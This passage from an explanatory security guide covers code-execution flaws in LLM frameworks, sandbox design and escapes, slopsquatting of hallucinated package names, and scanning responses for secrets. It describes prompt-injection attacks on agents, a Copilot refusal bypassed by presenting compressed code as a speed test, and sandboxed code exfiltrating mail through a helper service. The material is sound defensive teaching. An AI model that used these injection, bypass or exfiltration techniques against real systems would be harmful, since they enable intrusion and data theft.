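A Python program can do almost anything that the account running it may do, such as read files, start other programs and contact servers, whereas a database query can do only what the database allows. Products that have to run programs a model has written, such as data analysis tools and coding agents, need to confine those programs. Other applications run them by accident, because a developer used a Python interpreter for a small job that didn't need one, and the developer can usually remove the interpreter.

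### Answers passed to an interpreter

LangChain once had an arithmetic component, LLMMathChain, that asked the model to turn a question into Python and then ran the result. Asked to divide 551368 by 82, the model would write `551368 / 82`, and Python would return 6724. But LangChain ran the code with `exec`, which runs any Python program it receives as text, so anyone who could ask a question could try to make the model write a program that read the server's passwords. INCIBE's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023), a record kept by Spain's national cybersecurity institute, rates the flaw's severity at 9.8 out of 10.

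Vanna.AI, a library that answers questions about a database, had the same flaw in its charting feature. The model first wrote an SQL query. A second prompt, which included that query, then asked for Python code to chart the results, and Vanna ran the code with `exec`. JFrog's *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024) explains that the query had to be valid SQL or the database would reject it, so the researchers had the model write one that merely selected a quoted sentence. The sentence did nothing in the database, but in the second prompt the model treated it as an instruction and added the researchers' code to the chart program. A parser that checked the query would have found only a harmless `SELECT`. Vanna's maintainer responded to the report of this flaw, CVE-2024-5565, with a hardening guide, which protects only applications whose developers follow it.

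Tong Liu, a security researcher, found the Vanna flaw independently. Liu, Deng and colleagues (2023), in *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps*, searched systematically for such mistakes. RCE, or remote code execution, means that an outsider gets a computer to run code of their choice. Their tool, LLMSmith, searches a framework's source code for call chains, sequences of function calls that lead from a feature an app developer would use to a function that runs code. It found 51 chains in 11 frameworks, and 44 of them could run arbitrary code. The researchers counted 20 separate flaws, of which 19 allowed code execution and one allowed reading and writing files. The frameworks' developers confirmed 17 of the flaws.

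Liu and colleagues then tested 51 public apps in stages. They checked whether each app ran code at all, tried to make it run their own code, and tested whether it could contact an outside server and download a program that would give them lasting control. They broke into 17 apps, 16 through code execution and one through SQL injection. They could take lasting control of the server in 14 apps and get full administrator rights in four.

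The researchers looked for apps that seemed likely to run code, so their one-in-three success rate doesn't apply to language model apps in general. The attacks worked on 14 of the 24 apps whose source code was available and on three of the other 27. Of the 34 apps on which the attacks failed, 13 were malfunctioning and ten couldn't run code. The researchers could identify a protection against hostile code in only two.

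Models have become harder to manipulate since then, but frameworks still make the same mistake. In May, Microsoft (2026) described CVE-2026-26030, a flaw in its own agent framework, Semantic Kernel. In the researchers' demonstration, an agent searched a list of hotels. The model supplied the city, and the framework put it into a line of Python:

```
lambda x: x.city == 'Paris'
```

This defines a small function that checks whether hotel `x` is in Paris. The framework ran the line with `eval`, which calculates the value of a Python expression. Because the framework copied the city name in unchanged, an attacker could use a quotation mark in the name to add code, as in the shop's SQL query. MITRE's *Microsoft Semantic Kernel InMemoryVectorStore filter functionality vulnerable to remote code execution* (2026) classifies the flaw as CWE-94, code injection, and rates its severity at 10, the maximum.

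Semantic Kernel is not unusual in having security flaws. Callahan reports in *Agent Frameworks Fail Security Boundary Test* that in August 2026 Check Point disclosed 11 flaws in six agent frameworks, including LangChain, CrewAI and Google's Agent Development Kit. The flaws included old types such as path traversal and server-side request forgery.

### Why lists of forbidden words fail

Semantic Kernel's developers had foreseen that someone might inject code into the filter. Before running the filter, the framework parsed it into a syntax tree and rejected it if it contained any name on a list of dangerous ones, such as `exec` and `open`. It also ran the filter without access to Python's built-in functions.

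Microsoft's researchers got past both the check for forbidden names and the removal of built-in functions. Every value in Python links to its type, and types link to one another, so code can start from an ordinary value and follow these links to a component that loads other modules. Several of the names the code needed weren't on the forbidden list, and it never called a built-in function. The check also looked for forbidden names after a dot but not inside square brackets, where Python accepts many of the same names, though the researchers didn't need this gap.

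The developers could have added the missing names to the blocklist, but they would have had to be sure that no others were missing. Omissions from an allow-list are easier to discover because they break legitimate filters and users complain, while a gap in a blocklist lets attacks through and goes unnoticed until someone uses it. Microsoft's repair, in version 1.39.4, therefore permits only comparisons, logic, arithmetic, fixed values, a few safe functions and the filter's own variable. It keeps a blocklist as a further precaution.

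The framework could have searched by city without generating code. An ordinary function can compare `hotel.city` with a variable that holds the model's text, so the text is never run as code. The variable does the same job as the placeholder in a parameterised query.

Liu and colleagues found similar weaknesses in other filters. PandasAI, a data analysis library, limited the words and functions that generated code could use, but the researchers got around the limits with features built into Python. The developers of LlamaIndex, another framework, fixed a flaw the researchers had reported, but the researchers got around the fix through a third-party library. Even if a filter allowed only pandas, a popular library for working with tables, generated code could still use it to read and write files.

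A model's judgment of whether code is safe to run is not dependable. In *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (2026), Ori Lahav of the data security company Rubrik reports that Microsoft 365 Copilot declined to run code that listed the programs running in its sandbox. It usually ran the same code when a prompt presented it in compressed form as part of a speed test. In rare cases, Copilot unpacked the code to look at it first, and then refused to run it.

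### A calculator in place of an interpreter

LangChain repaired its arithmetic component by replacing `exec` with numexpr, a library that evaluates numerical expressions. The idea is sound because a language limited to arithmetic has no way to express an operation such as opening a file, so an attacker who controls the whole expression can still get only a number.

The first repair was weaker than it looked, because numexpr itself passed the expression to `eval`. This led to a second flaw, CVE-2023-39631, which GitLab's *CVE-2023-39631* (2023) dates to September 2023. According to Miggo's *CVE-2023-39631*, numexpr 2.8.5 fixed it by rejecting any expression that contains a semicolon, a colon, an opening square bracket or two underscores in a row. This is also a blocklist, but it is more defensible than Semantic Kernel's because ordinary arithmetic needs none of these characters. LangChain's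 current documentation for the component, *LLMMathChain*, advises developers to stop using it and shows a calculator tool as a replacement. That tool still uses numexpr, and supplies only the names `pi` and `e`.

A stricter calculator never calls `eval`. It parses the expression into a tree, rejects anything except numbers and the four basic operations, and calculates the result itself. For `551368 / 82`, the tree has division at the root and the two numbers as leaves. If the calculator also allows powers, it needs a limit on the size of the result. The expression `9**9**9` has only seven characters, but its value has about 370 million digits, and computing it could occupy the server for a long time.

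### What a sandbox has to restrict

The office assistant could use a calculator to add up the paper supplier's invoices, but when an employee asks which suppliers tend to invoice twice for the same order, it needs to write and run a program. The company has to assume that a supplier's email may have influenced the program.

The only files copied from the shared drive into the sandbox should be the invoices the task needs. The sandbox shouldn't contain passwords or access keys. Liu and colleagues note that most apps keep their keys in environment variables, settings that any program running under the same account can usually read. If the program needs information from another system, the application can fetch it beforehand and put only the result in the sandbox.

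The program should run under an account with few rights, so that it can't inspect or stop the server's other processes or gain administrator rights. On Linux, Liu and colleagues recommend `seccomp`, which limits the requests a program can make to the operating system, and `setrlimit`, which caps resources such as memory and processor time. A program that merely waits uses almost no processor time, so something outside the sandbox also has to shut the program down after a set amount of elapsed time.

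Most data analysis needs no network access, and blocking it entirely is the easiest rule to test. If a program needs some access, the restrictions have to cover services on its own computer as well as the internet, because local services may trust any request from the same computer. In June, Microsoft (2026) described a flaw in a development version of AutoGen Studio, a tool for building agents, that let an agent browsing untrusted pages reach a privileged service on its own computer. Microsoft fixed it before the affected part appeared in a packaged release.

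Changes that a program leaves behind can affect later users. Liu and colleagues took over an app they had set up on their own computer and changed its main program file. They could then replace the answers that other users received and record the access keys those users entered. If the office assistant reused one sandbox for all employees, a program from one employee's session could alter the next employee's results in the same way. The simplest remedy is to destroy the sandbox after each task and start the next task from a clean copy.

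### Containers, micro-virtual machines and WebAssembly

Developers usually build a sandbox with one of three technologies, which differ in what separates the program from the rest of the computer. The kernel, the core of the operating system, controls access to files, memory and devices, so an attacker who takes over the host's kernel controls the host.

| Technology | What separates the program from the host | What can break the separation | Main cost |
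|---|---|---|---|
| Container | The host's own kernel, which hides other files and processes from the program | A flaw in the shared kernel, or a container with too many rights | Limits are easy to set too loosely |
| Micro-virtual machine | A separate kernel for each sandbox, and a small program that gives it simulated hardware | A flaw in the processor's isolation or the simulated hardware | More memory and setup |
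| WebAssembly | A runtime that keeps the program in its own memory and offers it only chosen functions | A flaw in the runtime, or an offered function that does too much | Fewer libraries work |

Micro-virtual machines are generally the safest choice for unknown code that needs a full operating system, because a hostile program that compromises its own kernel is still inside the virtual machine. Containers start quickly and suit ordinary server software, but all their system calls go to a kernel they share with the host.

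Lahav exploited a service on the host to escape from the container that ran Copilot's Python code, and eventually reached the user's Microsoft 365 data. Microsoft Security Response Center's *CVE-2026-32193 Azure Kubernetes Service (AKS) Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* explains that a container sharing the host's network could send crafted requests to the service, which wasn't meant to accept them without a login. A path traversal flaw in the service let an attacker take control of the host. Microsoft published the fix on 9 June 2026 and knew of no attacks that had used the flaw. A separate kernel might not have prevented the escape if the sandbox could still reach that service.

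In Liu and colleagues' study, the two protected apps used Pyodide, a version of Python that runs on WebAssembly in the user's browser. Generated code never ran on the company's server, so it couldn't damage the server. However, Pyodide supports only some Python libraries and can be very slow to load the first time.

Liu and colleagues write that running the code in the user's browser with Pyodide fundamentally resolves the flaw. This protects the server but not the user, because Pyodide lets Python programs call the page's JavaScript functions. If a supplier's email influenced the program, the result would amount to cross-site scripting (XSS). The application should therefore run Pyodide in a sandboxed frame on a separate domain, as it would a generated web page.

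### The helper outside Copilot Cowork's sandbox

Copilot Cowork is a Microsoft agent that works with an employee's email, files and Teams chats, and runs code in a sandbox without internet access. Microsoft gave the sandbox a helper service that copied files in and out. The service ran outside the sandbox, could reach the internet, and accepted a web address for the file to copy.

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* reports that a program inside the sandbox could give the service any address. The program could therefore fetch commands from an attacker's server and send the results back in the address of its next request. Bing and Teams relayed stolen data for Copilot in a similar way. In ReLeak, code in a Copilot sandbox also reached an outside server despite a ban on network traffic.

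In PromptArmor's demonstration, the hostile program came with a Skill that the employee had found online. The program compared two documents for inconsistencies, as advertised, and contacted the attacker in the background. Programs in the sandbox could also use Cowork's connections to Outlook and SharePoint, and only the network ban kept the mailbox private. One helper defeated that ban, so the attacker could list and read the employee's messages.

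Pressing the stop button didn't help, because it ended the agent's turn but not the processes running in the background. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had mitigated it. A developer building a similar service can avoid the problem by having the service accept the number of a known file instead of a web address, and any stop button should shut down the whole sandbox.

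### Code that runs later

A sandbox confines a program only while the program runs inside it. Semantic Kernel's second flaw, CVE-2026-25592, shows how a file can leave a working sandbox and run elsewhere. The framework ran generated Python in an isolated cloud service, and helper functions on the host copied files in and out. In the version for Microsoft's .NET platform, a developer had mistakenly labelled the download function as a tool, so the model could call it and choose where on the host to save the file.

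An attacker could get the model to write a script in the sandbox and then download it to the host's Windows Startup folder, whose programs run whenever the user signs in. Neither step looked like an escape, because the model had only created a file in the sandbox and the framework had only saved one on the host. The script ran at the next sign-in, outside the sandbox and without the model's involvement.

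Microsoft removed the label in version 1.71.0, so the model can no longer call the function. If a developer's own code calls it, the function now works out the full path and checks it against a list of permitted folders. A similar upload function had accepted any file on the host, which could have put private keys into the sandbox. Microsoft added optional checks to that function too.

Build systems create a similar delay in software companies. A build system turns source code into a finished program and runs its tests, often automatically and with access to the keys needed to publish the result. Suppose an attacker plants a fake setup step in a library's instructions, and a coding agent copies it into a project's build script. The agent's sandbox allows this because the agent is supposed to edit project files. When the build server runs the script that night, the attacker's command runs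 with access to the publishing keys. *Cuckoo Attack* (2025), a paper on persistent attacks against AI code editors, lists project description files, technical forums and developers' blogs as places where outsiders can plant such text.

Some files control the sandbox itself. Liu and colleagues describe an older flaw in AutoGPT, which ran each piece of generated code in a separate container. An attacker could escape the container by overwriting the file that held its settings.

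A company can reduce the danger by treating certain files as code, whatever their format, including build scripts, editor settings, startup files and anything that configures the sandbox. The agent should need a person's approval to change these files, or have no write access to them at all. The company should also build unreviewed changes in a separate sandbox that has no publishing keys. A similar rule should apply to the office assistant, because a script that it saves to the shared drive will run with the rights of whichever colleague opens it.

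### Security flaws in code that works

Someone has to review the code for a generated login page before a company puts it on its website, because the page can work and still be open to SQL injection. Running the code in a sandbox first does not fix this, since the vulnerability will still be there when the page is deployed.

Static analysis, which examines source code without running it, can catch some vulnerabilities. For example, it can trace a visitor's input through the program to see whether the input reaches a database query without a placeholder. *Large Language Models (LLMs) for Source Code Analysis* (2025) describes a system called SecCode that passes the findings of the analysis tool CodeQL back to the model, which rewrites the code until CodeQL finds no more problems.

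The method misses the flaws that CodeQL misses. *Can LLM Prompting Serve as a Proxy for Static Analysis* (2024) says that static analysis tools are error-prone and struggle with partial code, which coding assistants often produce. On such fragments, models did better than Amazon's CodeGuru Security tool when the prompt specified which security properties to check. But *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (2026) describes a system that gives models written security specifications because standard models fail to distinguish vulnerable code from the repaired version without them.

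These errors also affect any estimate of how often models write insecure code. Suppose a model writes 1,000 functions, 50 of them flawed. An analyser finds 40 of the 50 and wrongly flags 95 of the 950 sound ones. It reports 135 flawed functions, or 13.5%, when the true rate is 5%, and fewer than a third of its warnings are correct. If the model then rewrites the flagged functions until the warnings stop, the analyser reports a rate of 0%, although the ten flawed functions it missed remain.

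The choice of tasks can change the result just as much. A test made up of login pages and file uploads will produce more flaws than a typical week of programming, so its flaw rate shouldn't be applied to all of a company's generated code. A useful measurement needs tasks similar to the company's own. It also needs to check for flaws with a method the model didn't use while writing the code, such as tests that try to exploit the finished program.

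Static analysis is best at finding flaws with a recognisable pattern, such as untrusted text in a query or a call to `eval`. It is much weaker at finding missing permission checks, such as the public chatbot's failure to check whose order it was looking up, because the code may contain no suspicious function. A reviewer who knows that customers should see only their own orders can notice the missing check and write a test that logs in as one customer and asks for another's order.

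## Package names that a model has invented

Most programs use packages, which are collections of code that other people have published. A model that writes a program usually chooses its packages too. A reviewer can read all 50 lines of a generated program and find nothing wrong, even though one of those lines imports thousands more that a stranger wrote.

### From a name to running code

Suppose the office assistant writes a program that extracts tables from PDF invoices, and the program needs a package that isn't on the server. The assistant runs `pip install` followed by the package's name. Pip, Python's package manager, looks up the name in PyPI, the public registry of Python packages. It normally downloads the newest version compatible with the computer, along with any other packages that version depends on. JavaScript developers do the same with npm, which is the name of both a package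 manager and a registry.

The downloaded code can run before any program uses it. An npm package can include scripts that run during installation, and a Python package supplied as source code can include build steps that pip runs. These scripts and build steps run with the permissions of the account that started the installation, which on a developer's computer often include access to passwords and publishing keys. If a package has neither, its code runs when a program first imports it.

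The package manager is the sink, and it usually has only the name to identify a package. Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, notes that anyone with an email address can publish on PyPI or npm, and that neither registry reviews first-time uploads. An unused name generally goes to the first person who publishes under it.

A model can combine familiar pieces into a plausible name that belongs to no package. The installation fails if nobody has registered the name, but if an attacker has, the same command installs the attacker's code. The attack doesn't require prompt injection, because the model makes the mistake when answering an ordinary question. An attacker can also encourage the mistake, as *Trust Me, Import This* (2026) demonstrates with malicious skill files for coding agents.

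### Slopsquatting and two older attacks

Slopsquatting means registering a package name that models tend to invent. *Bayesian-Calibrated Detection of Hallucinated Package Imports in AI-Assisted Code* (2026) credits Seth Larson of the Python Software Foundation with coining the word and Andrew Nesbitt with popularising it.

The word "slopsquatting" is a play on typosquatting, in which an attacker registers a misspelling of a popular package and waits for someone to mistype the name. tianpan.co's *The Package Your Agent Hallucinated Now Exists — and It's Malicious* (2026) gives the example of `requets` for `requests`. Anyone can ask a model thousands of programming questions and collect the package names it invents, so a slopsquatter doesn't have to guess at people's typing errors. Churilov's experiment, which covered five models, cost about $1,160.

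In dependency confusion, the name is correct but the package comes from the wrong place. An attacker publishes a package on a public registry under the same name as a company's private package. A package manager that searches both registries and takes the highest version number will install the attacker's package if its number is higher. Sonatype's *Inside a 176-Package npm Campaign Built to Beat Your Internal Dependencies* (2026) describes malicious packages of this kind, many of them numbered 99.99.99 to exceed any real version number.

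### The 2024 measurements

Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues published the first large study, *We Have a Package for You!*, in 2024 and presented it at the USENIX Security conference in 2025. They had 16 models generate 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code. Half of the prompts were questions from the programming site Stack Overflow, and a model wrote the other half from descriptions of popular packages.

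Import statements don't always identify the packages a program needs, because they name modules, and a module can have a different name from the package that contains it. Python's `PIL` module, for example, comes from the Pillow package. Spracklen and colleagues therefore collected names from installation commands and asked each model twice which packages were necessary. They compared the names with lists of every package on PyPI and npm as of 10 January 2024.

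The models named packages 2.23 million times, and in 440,445 of those cases (19.7%) the package didn't exist. These cases included 205,474 different invented names. The rate was 5.2% for the three commercial models, all from OpenAI, and 21.7% for the 13 open ones. GPT-4 Turbo had the lowest rate, at 3.59%.

Attackers benefit most from invented names that appear repeatedly. The researchers took 500 prompts that had produced an invented name and ran each one ten more times. For 43% of the prompts, the same name appeared in all ten runs, and for 39% it never reappeared. Models still invented names when they chose only the most likely tokens, which suggests that many of these names are a model's most likely output and not a result of random sampling.

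When one model repeatedly invented a name, other models usually did not invent it. Only 19% of the invented names came from more than one model. Of the invented Python package names, 8.7% belonged to real JavaScript packages on npm, and just 0.17% belonged to packages deleted from PyPI.

### Newer models

Churilov ran the same prompts on five newer models in April 2026 and checked the names against the live registries in November. The table shows invented names as a share of all package names the models gave.

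| Models | Year of test | Invented names |
|---|---|---|
| Three commercial models (Spracklen and colleagues) | 2024 | 5.2% |
| 13 open models (Spracklen and colleagues) | 2024 | 21.7% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 (Churilov) | 2026 | 3.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 (Churilov) | 2026 | 4.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro (Churilov) | 2026 | 4.8% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, an open model (Churilov) | 2026 | 4.8% |
| GPT-5.4-mini (Churilov) | 2026 | 5.0% |

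None of the newer models improved on the best 2024 result, GPT-4 Turbo's 3.59%, although Claude Haiku 4.5 came close at 3.63%. The comparison is rough, because Churilov took names from installation commands and import statements instead of asking the models to list packages. The old prompts had also been public since January 2025, so the newer models may have seen them in training, which would make their rates misleadingly low. Churilov didn't test the stronger models that OpenAI, Anthropic and Google have since released, such as GPT-6 Astra.

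DeepSeek's result suggests that the 2024 gap had more to do with the open models' capability than with their openness. Weak models still do badly. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) reports an average hallucination rate of 24.7% for Python across eight models, some of them very small. Letting the models consult relevant package information cut this to 11.5%.

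The measured rate of invented packages depends almost as much on the counting method as on the model. Counting modules that come with Python as invented packages would have raised the eight-model average to 32.3%. Churilov's first figures, 4.6% to 6.1%, were too high mainly because they included correct import statements for modules whose names differ from their package names.

All five of Churilov's models invented the same 104 names. An attacker who registered one of these could reach users of models from four companies. Of the 104 names, 54 were one character away from a real package's name, so a filter designed for typosquatting might catch them. Allowing two characters of difference would flag 81, but this means little on registries so crowded that most short names are close to a real one. In 2024, only 13.4% of the invented Python names were within two characters of a real one.

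### Agents that can look things up

A coding agent can search for a package before installing it. *Slopsquatting*, Park's 2025 report for the security company Trend Micro, tested three coding tools on the ten tasks where plain models had invented the most names. Claude Code and Codex CLI invented roughly half as many names as the plain models. Cursor, which had extra tools for searching the web and reading current documentation, invented even fewer, but it occasionally used a name that belonged to a JavaScript package or to no package. Park ran the tasks by hand, and ten tasks are too few to give a reliable rate.

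Spira, Cohen and colleagues (2026), in *Beware of Agentic Botnets*, ran a much larger test on a related problem. They asked agents to download projects from GitHub by name alone, such as "clone librepods". A GitHub address also contains the owner's name, which the agent has to find or guess. Six models working without tools gave a wrong address 92.4% of the time for ten recent projects and 0.9% of the time for five old and famous ones.

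In 1,381 runs with the agent Cursor CLI, the address was correct 93.4% of the time when the agent searched first and 0.9% when it didn't. The agent skipped the search in about a third of these runs. Whether it searched depended on the model and the wording of the request. Claude Sonnet 4.5 never searched when told to "clone" librepods, but usually did when asked to print a command for cloning it.

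These rates don't apply directly to PyPI and npm, where a package has no owner's name to guess and most requests are for well-known packages. But they show why an application shouldn't let the model decide whether to look up a package. The application can require a lookup in ordinary code before every installation. A lookup may find an attacker's package once it exists, so the application still has to decide which results are acceptable.

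### What a small error rate adds up to

Suppose a careful setup reduces the share of invented names to 0.5%. If an agent makes 50 independent suggestions, the chance that at least one name is invented is 1 − 0.995⁵⁰, or about 22%. At 4%, close to the rates in Churilov's tests, the chance would be 87%.

In practice, a model's package suggestions aren't independent. A developer who asks only for common packages may never see an invented name, while one who works with new or obscure tools may see several. The same question often produces the same invented name, so asking it 50 times adds less risk than asking 50 different questions.

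An invented name also does no harm unless somebody has registered it. Churilov found that people had registered 25 of 2,282 invented names, about 1%, within roughly six months. If all of those packages had contained malware, a model that invented 0.5% of the names it suggested would make one dangerous suggestion in 20,000. Someone who installed 50 suggested packages would have about a 0.25% chance of installing a dangerous one, but a company whose agents installed 100,000 a year could expect five. This estimate is too high in one respect, because most of the 25 aren't known to be malicious, but it could be too low overall because attackers can choose the names that models suggest most often.

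### Demonstrations and real malware

Researchers have registered package names that models invented to see who would install them, and attackers have published plenty of malware under plausible names. There is much less evidence of attackers publishing malware under names that a model invented.

| Case | Did a model invent the name? | What the package did |
|---|---|---|
| `huggingface-cli`, 2023–24 | Models repeatedly suggested it | Nothing, since a researcher had left it empty |
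| `react-codeshift`, 2026 | Very probably | Nothing, since a researcher had left it empty |
| Names in companies' documentation for agents, 2026 | Not necessarily | Contacted the researchers' server |
| One npm name in Churilov's results, 2026 | Yes | Contained malware, and npm removed it |
| Near miss at the company Softjourn, 2026 | Yes, by an unconfirmed account | Contained malware, by the same account |
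| Flooding Dropper, 2026 | No known link | Installed malware |

Bar Lanyado described the best-known test in *Diving Deeper into AI Package Hallucinations*, published in March 2024. Models kept recommending `pip install huggingface-cli`, although no package of that name existed, so Lanyado published an empty one. Security scanners download almost everything that appears on PyPI, so Lanyado also published a package with a meaningless name to account for their downloads. After three months, Lanyado counted more than 30,000 genuine downloads of the first package. A research project by the Chinese technology company Alibaba included it in its installation instructions.

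The downloads don't show that 30,000 people followed a model's advice. *Hallucination Creates Security Holes* reports more than 15,000 downloads and says it is unclear how many resulted from generated code. The real command-line tool `huggingface-cli` comes with a package called `huggingface_hub`, so a person could easily guess the wrong package name without a model's help. Once the wrong name is in a project's instructions, an automated build can also download the package many times a day. Comparing the downloads with those of the package with the meaningless name doesn't correct for this, because no project's instructions mention that package.

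*Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands* (Eriksen, January 2026) traces how an invented package name spread through skills, which are instructions for agents. In October 2025, somebody added 47 model-written skills to a public GitHub project, apparently without reviewing them. At least two told agents to run `react-codeshift`, which looks like a blend of two real packages, `jscodeshift` and `react-codemod`. Other people copied the project, and one translated the skill into Japanese. By the time Eriksen registered the name, it was in 237 GitHub repositories.

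The empty package had about 74 downloads on its first day, which is normal for a new package that nobody uses, and then 12 over the next five days. Eriksen attributes the later downloads to agents following the skills, which is plausible because unused packages normally get none after the first day. However, the counts don't distinguish agents from curious people. The case shows more clearly that an invented name can spread beyond the conversation that produced it, because a model that would never have made up `react-codeshift` could still install it after reading the skill.

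A similar weakness affects `llms.txt` files, in which companies publish documentation for agents. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* reports that researchers found references to unclaimed names in such files on 120 domains. After they registered one, a Fortune 500 company's coding agent contacted their server within an hour, according to The News International's *AI coding agents can be tricked in under an hour, researchers find* (2026). Some of these names may be out of date rather than invented by models, so this is evidence only that agents follow documentation.

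Evidence of actual attacks is limited. In Churilov's tests, a model invented an npm package name that was later used for malware. This is the clearest case, but the attacker may have thought of the name independently. At least 23 other names that the models suggested had been used for malware before the tests began, and the models could have learned them from the malicious packages or from reports about them.

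Churchill (2026), in *Nearly one in five packages an AI names do not exist*, gives a second-hand account of an engineer at Softjourn who nearly installed malware that an agent had recommended. The engineer followed a company rule to check such packages by hand, saw that the project was only days old, and stopped. Sonatype's *'Flooding Dropper' Campaign Hits npm With Nearly 850 Malicious Packages* (2026) documents malware in detail, but doesn't connect the package names to models.

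From 30 April to 7 November 2026, Churilov accidentally left public the list of package names that all the models had invented. This allowed a test of whether attackers use such lists. In the main comparison, nobody registered any of 87 published names, and people registered two of 101 similar names that had stayed private. The study could have detected only a large effect, but there was clearly no rush to register the published names. It also had no comparison group of plausible names that models don't invent, so the 1% registration rate may be no higher than for other plausible names.

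### Why checking that a name exists doesn't help

OWASP advises developers to verify the packages a model suggests. Checking only that the name exists in the registry does not protect against slopsquatting. If the name is unregistered, the lookup fails, but so would the installation. Once an attacker registers the name, the lookup succeeds.

A package that passes the lookup can also be harmless but unrelated to the task. Schipper (2026), in *Slopsquatting*, checked four names that researchers had cited as invented and found all four on PyPI. One was `tabula`, which a model may suggest for extracting tables from PDFs when the developer needs `tabula-py`. The `tabula` package formats plain-text tables and was last released in 2012.

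Looking up a package name is still worthwhile before publishing instructions, because it would have kept `react-codeshift` out of the original skills. Before installation, the check has to confirm that the package is the one the developer wanted. The most reliable source is the installation command on the project's own website. Lanyado also recommends checking a package's publication date, maintenance record and community. Download counts can mislead, since even an empty package can get 60 to 100 downloads on its first day.

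*PackMonitor* (2026) restricts package names to a permitted list while the model is writing them, much as constrained decoding forces output to fit a grammar. This can completely prevent the model from inventing names. But if the list is a copy of the whole public registry, it includes any packages that attackers had published before the copy was made.

### Approved registries and checks before installation

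A company can run its own registry that contains only packages it has approved. An invented name then fails to install even if an attacker has registered it publicly. Spracklen and colleagues call curated lists blunt, because somebody has to keep them up to date, but consider them more effective than checking whether a package exists. Maintaining the list is manageable for the office assistant, which might need 30 packages for analysing invoices. It is harder for a software company whose developers try new packages every week.

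An internal registry gives no such protection if it automatically fetches any missing package from PyPI or npm. The package manager must also use only the internal registry, or dependency confusion becomes possible. Setting this in a configuration file isn't enough for an agent, because it can name a different registry in its installation command. *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (2026) reports that coding agents install from untrusted registries almost unconditionally when a project's instructions tell them to. The company should therefore block the public registries at the network level.

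The same study proposes a hook, a small program that checks every installation command before it runs. The hook applies fixed rules to the package's name, source and version, so persuasive wording in an instruction file can't change the result. *YUL* (2026) reports that the hook caught 10 of 11 attack scenarios but checks only installation commands. An agent can also add a package name to a project's list of dependencies, which a build server installs later. *YUL* checks that list as the agent writes it.

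### Lockfiles, waiting periods and installation scripts

A lockfile records the exact version of every package in a project, usually with a hash, a short code computed from the package's contents. Later installations can use the same files and reject any that have changed. This stops an attacker from quietly replacing a package, but it doesn't protect the project when it first adds one. If an agent installs a slopsquatted package, the lockfile records it like any other, and later installations can reuse the same malware.

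Lockfiles help more if a person has to approve changes to them, because the reviewer sees a new package name before it reaches the build server. The server should refuse to install anything that isn't in the approved lockfile. These steps don't protect the agent's own computer if the agent has already installed the package there, so the agent should first install it in a sandbox without passwords or keys.

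Some companies wait a few days before accepting new packages, which gives security researchers time to find malware. Xygeni's *Malicious Code Digest 82* describes a campaign in which the attacker withdrew 19 of 20 packages within hours of their detection. A one-week wait would probably have avoided them. A slopsquatter can wait longer, though, because the name costs nothing to keep. The attacker can publish a harmless version first and add the malware months later.

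A rule should therefore set separate minimum ages for packages and versions. The company might require a package to have existed for six months, and accept new versions after a week. Urgent security fixes need an exception, because waiting would leave known flaws unpatched. The rule would have blocked the days-old package in the Softjourn story, but not one that an attacker had registered the year before and kept free of malware until recently.

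Blocking installation scripts stops packages from running code during installation. Python developers can get much the same protection by accepting only ready-built packages, which have no build step. Some legitimate packages stop working without their scripts, so the company has to allow exceptions. Blocking scripts didn't stop the malware in Xygeni's campaign, which ran when a program loaded the package, not during installation. It also wouldn't help with `npx`, the command in Eriksen's skills, which downloads a package and runs it straight away.

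### Names that nobody else can register

Registries can protect everyone by refusing to let outsiders register names that models are likely to invent. PyPI has a list of prohibited names. When Churilov sent PyPI more than 100 names that all five models had invented, its security team replied that this list and its rules on spelling variants left 41 open to registration. The security company Socket found that outsiders could register 12 of 18 names on npm. Four of the other six began with the name of an organisation that controls everything published under it. Lanyado found a similar protection in the registry for Microsoft's .NET platform, which reserves prefixes such as `Microsoft` and `Google`.

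No registry could reserve every invented name, since the 2024 study alone produced over 200,000. But in Churilov's results, the 104 shared names were under 5% of the distinct invented names and accounted for 42% of all the times a model gave one. Reserving those 104 would therefore remove much of the opportunity for attackers, at least for these models and prompts.

The list would need regular updates as models change, and some names would have to remain available to developers with a good reason to use them. Instead of blocking every name on the list, a registry could hold new packages with those names for review. It would also have to keep the list private, because attackers could register any name on it that was not yet blocked.

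## Scanning responses for secrets and personal data

Suppose an employee asks the office assistant how to order more paper, and the answer includes the password to the supplier's website, which a colleague once pasted into a shared document. Encoding the answer doesn't help, because the harm comes from disclosing the password to the reader or to whichever system receives the text next.

Response scanning means searching a model's output for secrets and personal data before it leaves the application. OWASP's *LLM02:2025 Sensitive Information Disclosure* describes the flaw this addresses, the exposure of personal and financial details, health records, confidential business data, legal documents and credentials such as passwords and access keys. A developer can use the system prompt, the standing instructions that come before each conversation, to forbid the model to reveal these, but OWASP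 warns that the model may not follow the instruction. Most of OWASP's other advice concerns what goes into the model. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre also recommends blocking sensitive patterns in responses, and Google's *Prevent sensitive information disclosure*, published by Android Developers, recommends redacting the final output. Both combine scanning with other controls.

### Where the data comes from

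| Source | Example of a leak | What a scanner can do |
|---|---|---|
| Training data | A stranger's phone number that the model memorised | Recognise the format, but not whether the number is real |
| Retrieved documents | A salary list in a folder with the wrong permissions | Find names and account numbers, but not tell whether this employee may see them |
| System prompt | An access key or internal instructions | Compare the reply with the exact text, which the developer has |
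| Tool results | A password in a database's error message | Find keys that are known or have a recognisable format |
| Another user's session | Someone else's order, from a shared cache | Very little, unless it can compare the details with the current user's account |

Much of what OWASP calls sensitive has no set format, so a scanner could not recognise a sentence like "We are closing the Leeds office in March" as confidential.

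Data can also leak outside the answer. According to HackerDNA, a security training company, OWASP's 2026 edition mentions tool arguments, logs and reasoning traces, which are the intermediate steps a model writes before its answer. In *Safer Reasoning Traces*, Ahrend, Eder and colleagues (2026) gave six models invented personal details and a policy against repeating them, then asked for the details. The models revealed them 52.3% of the time when asked directly and 86.3% when asked to reason step by step. Ordinary users rarely ask such questions, so these rates don't show how often models leak data in normal conversations.

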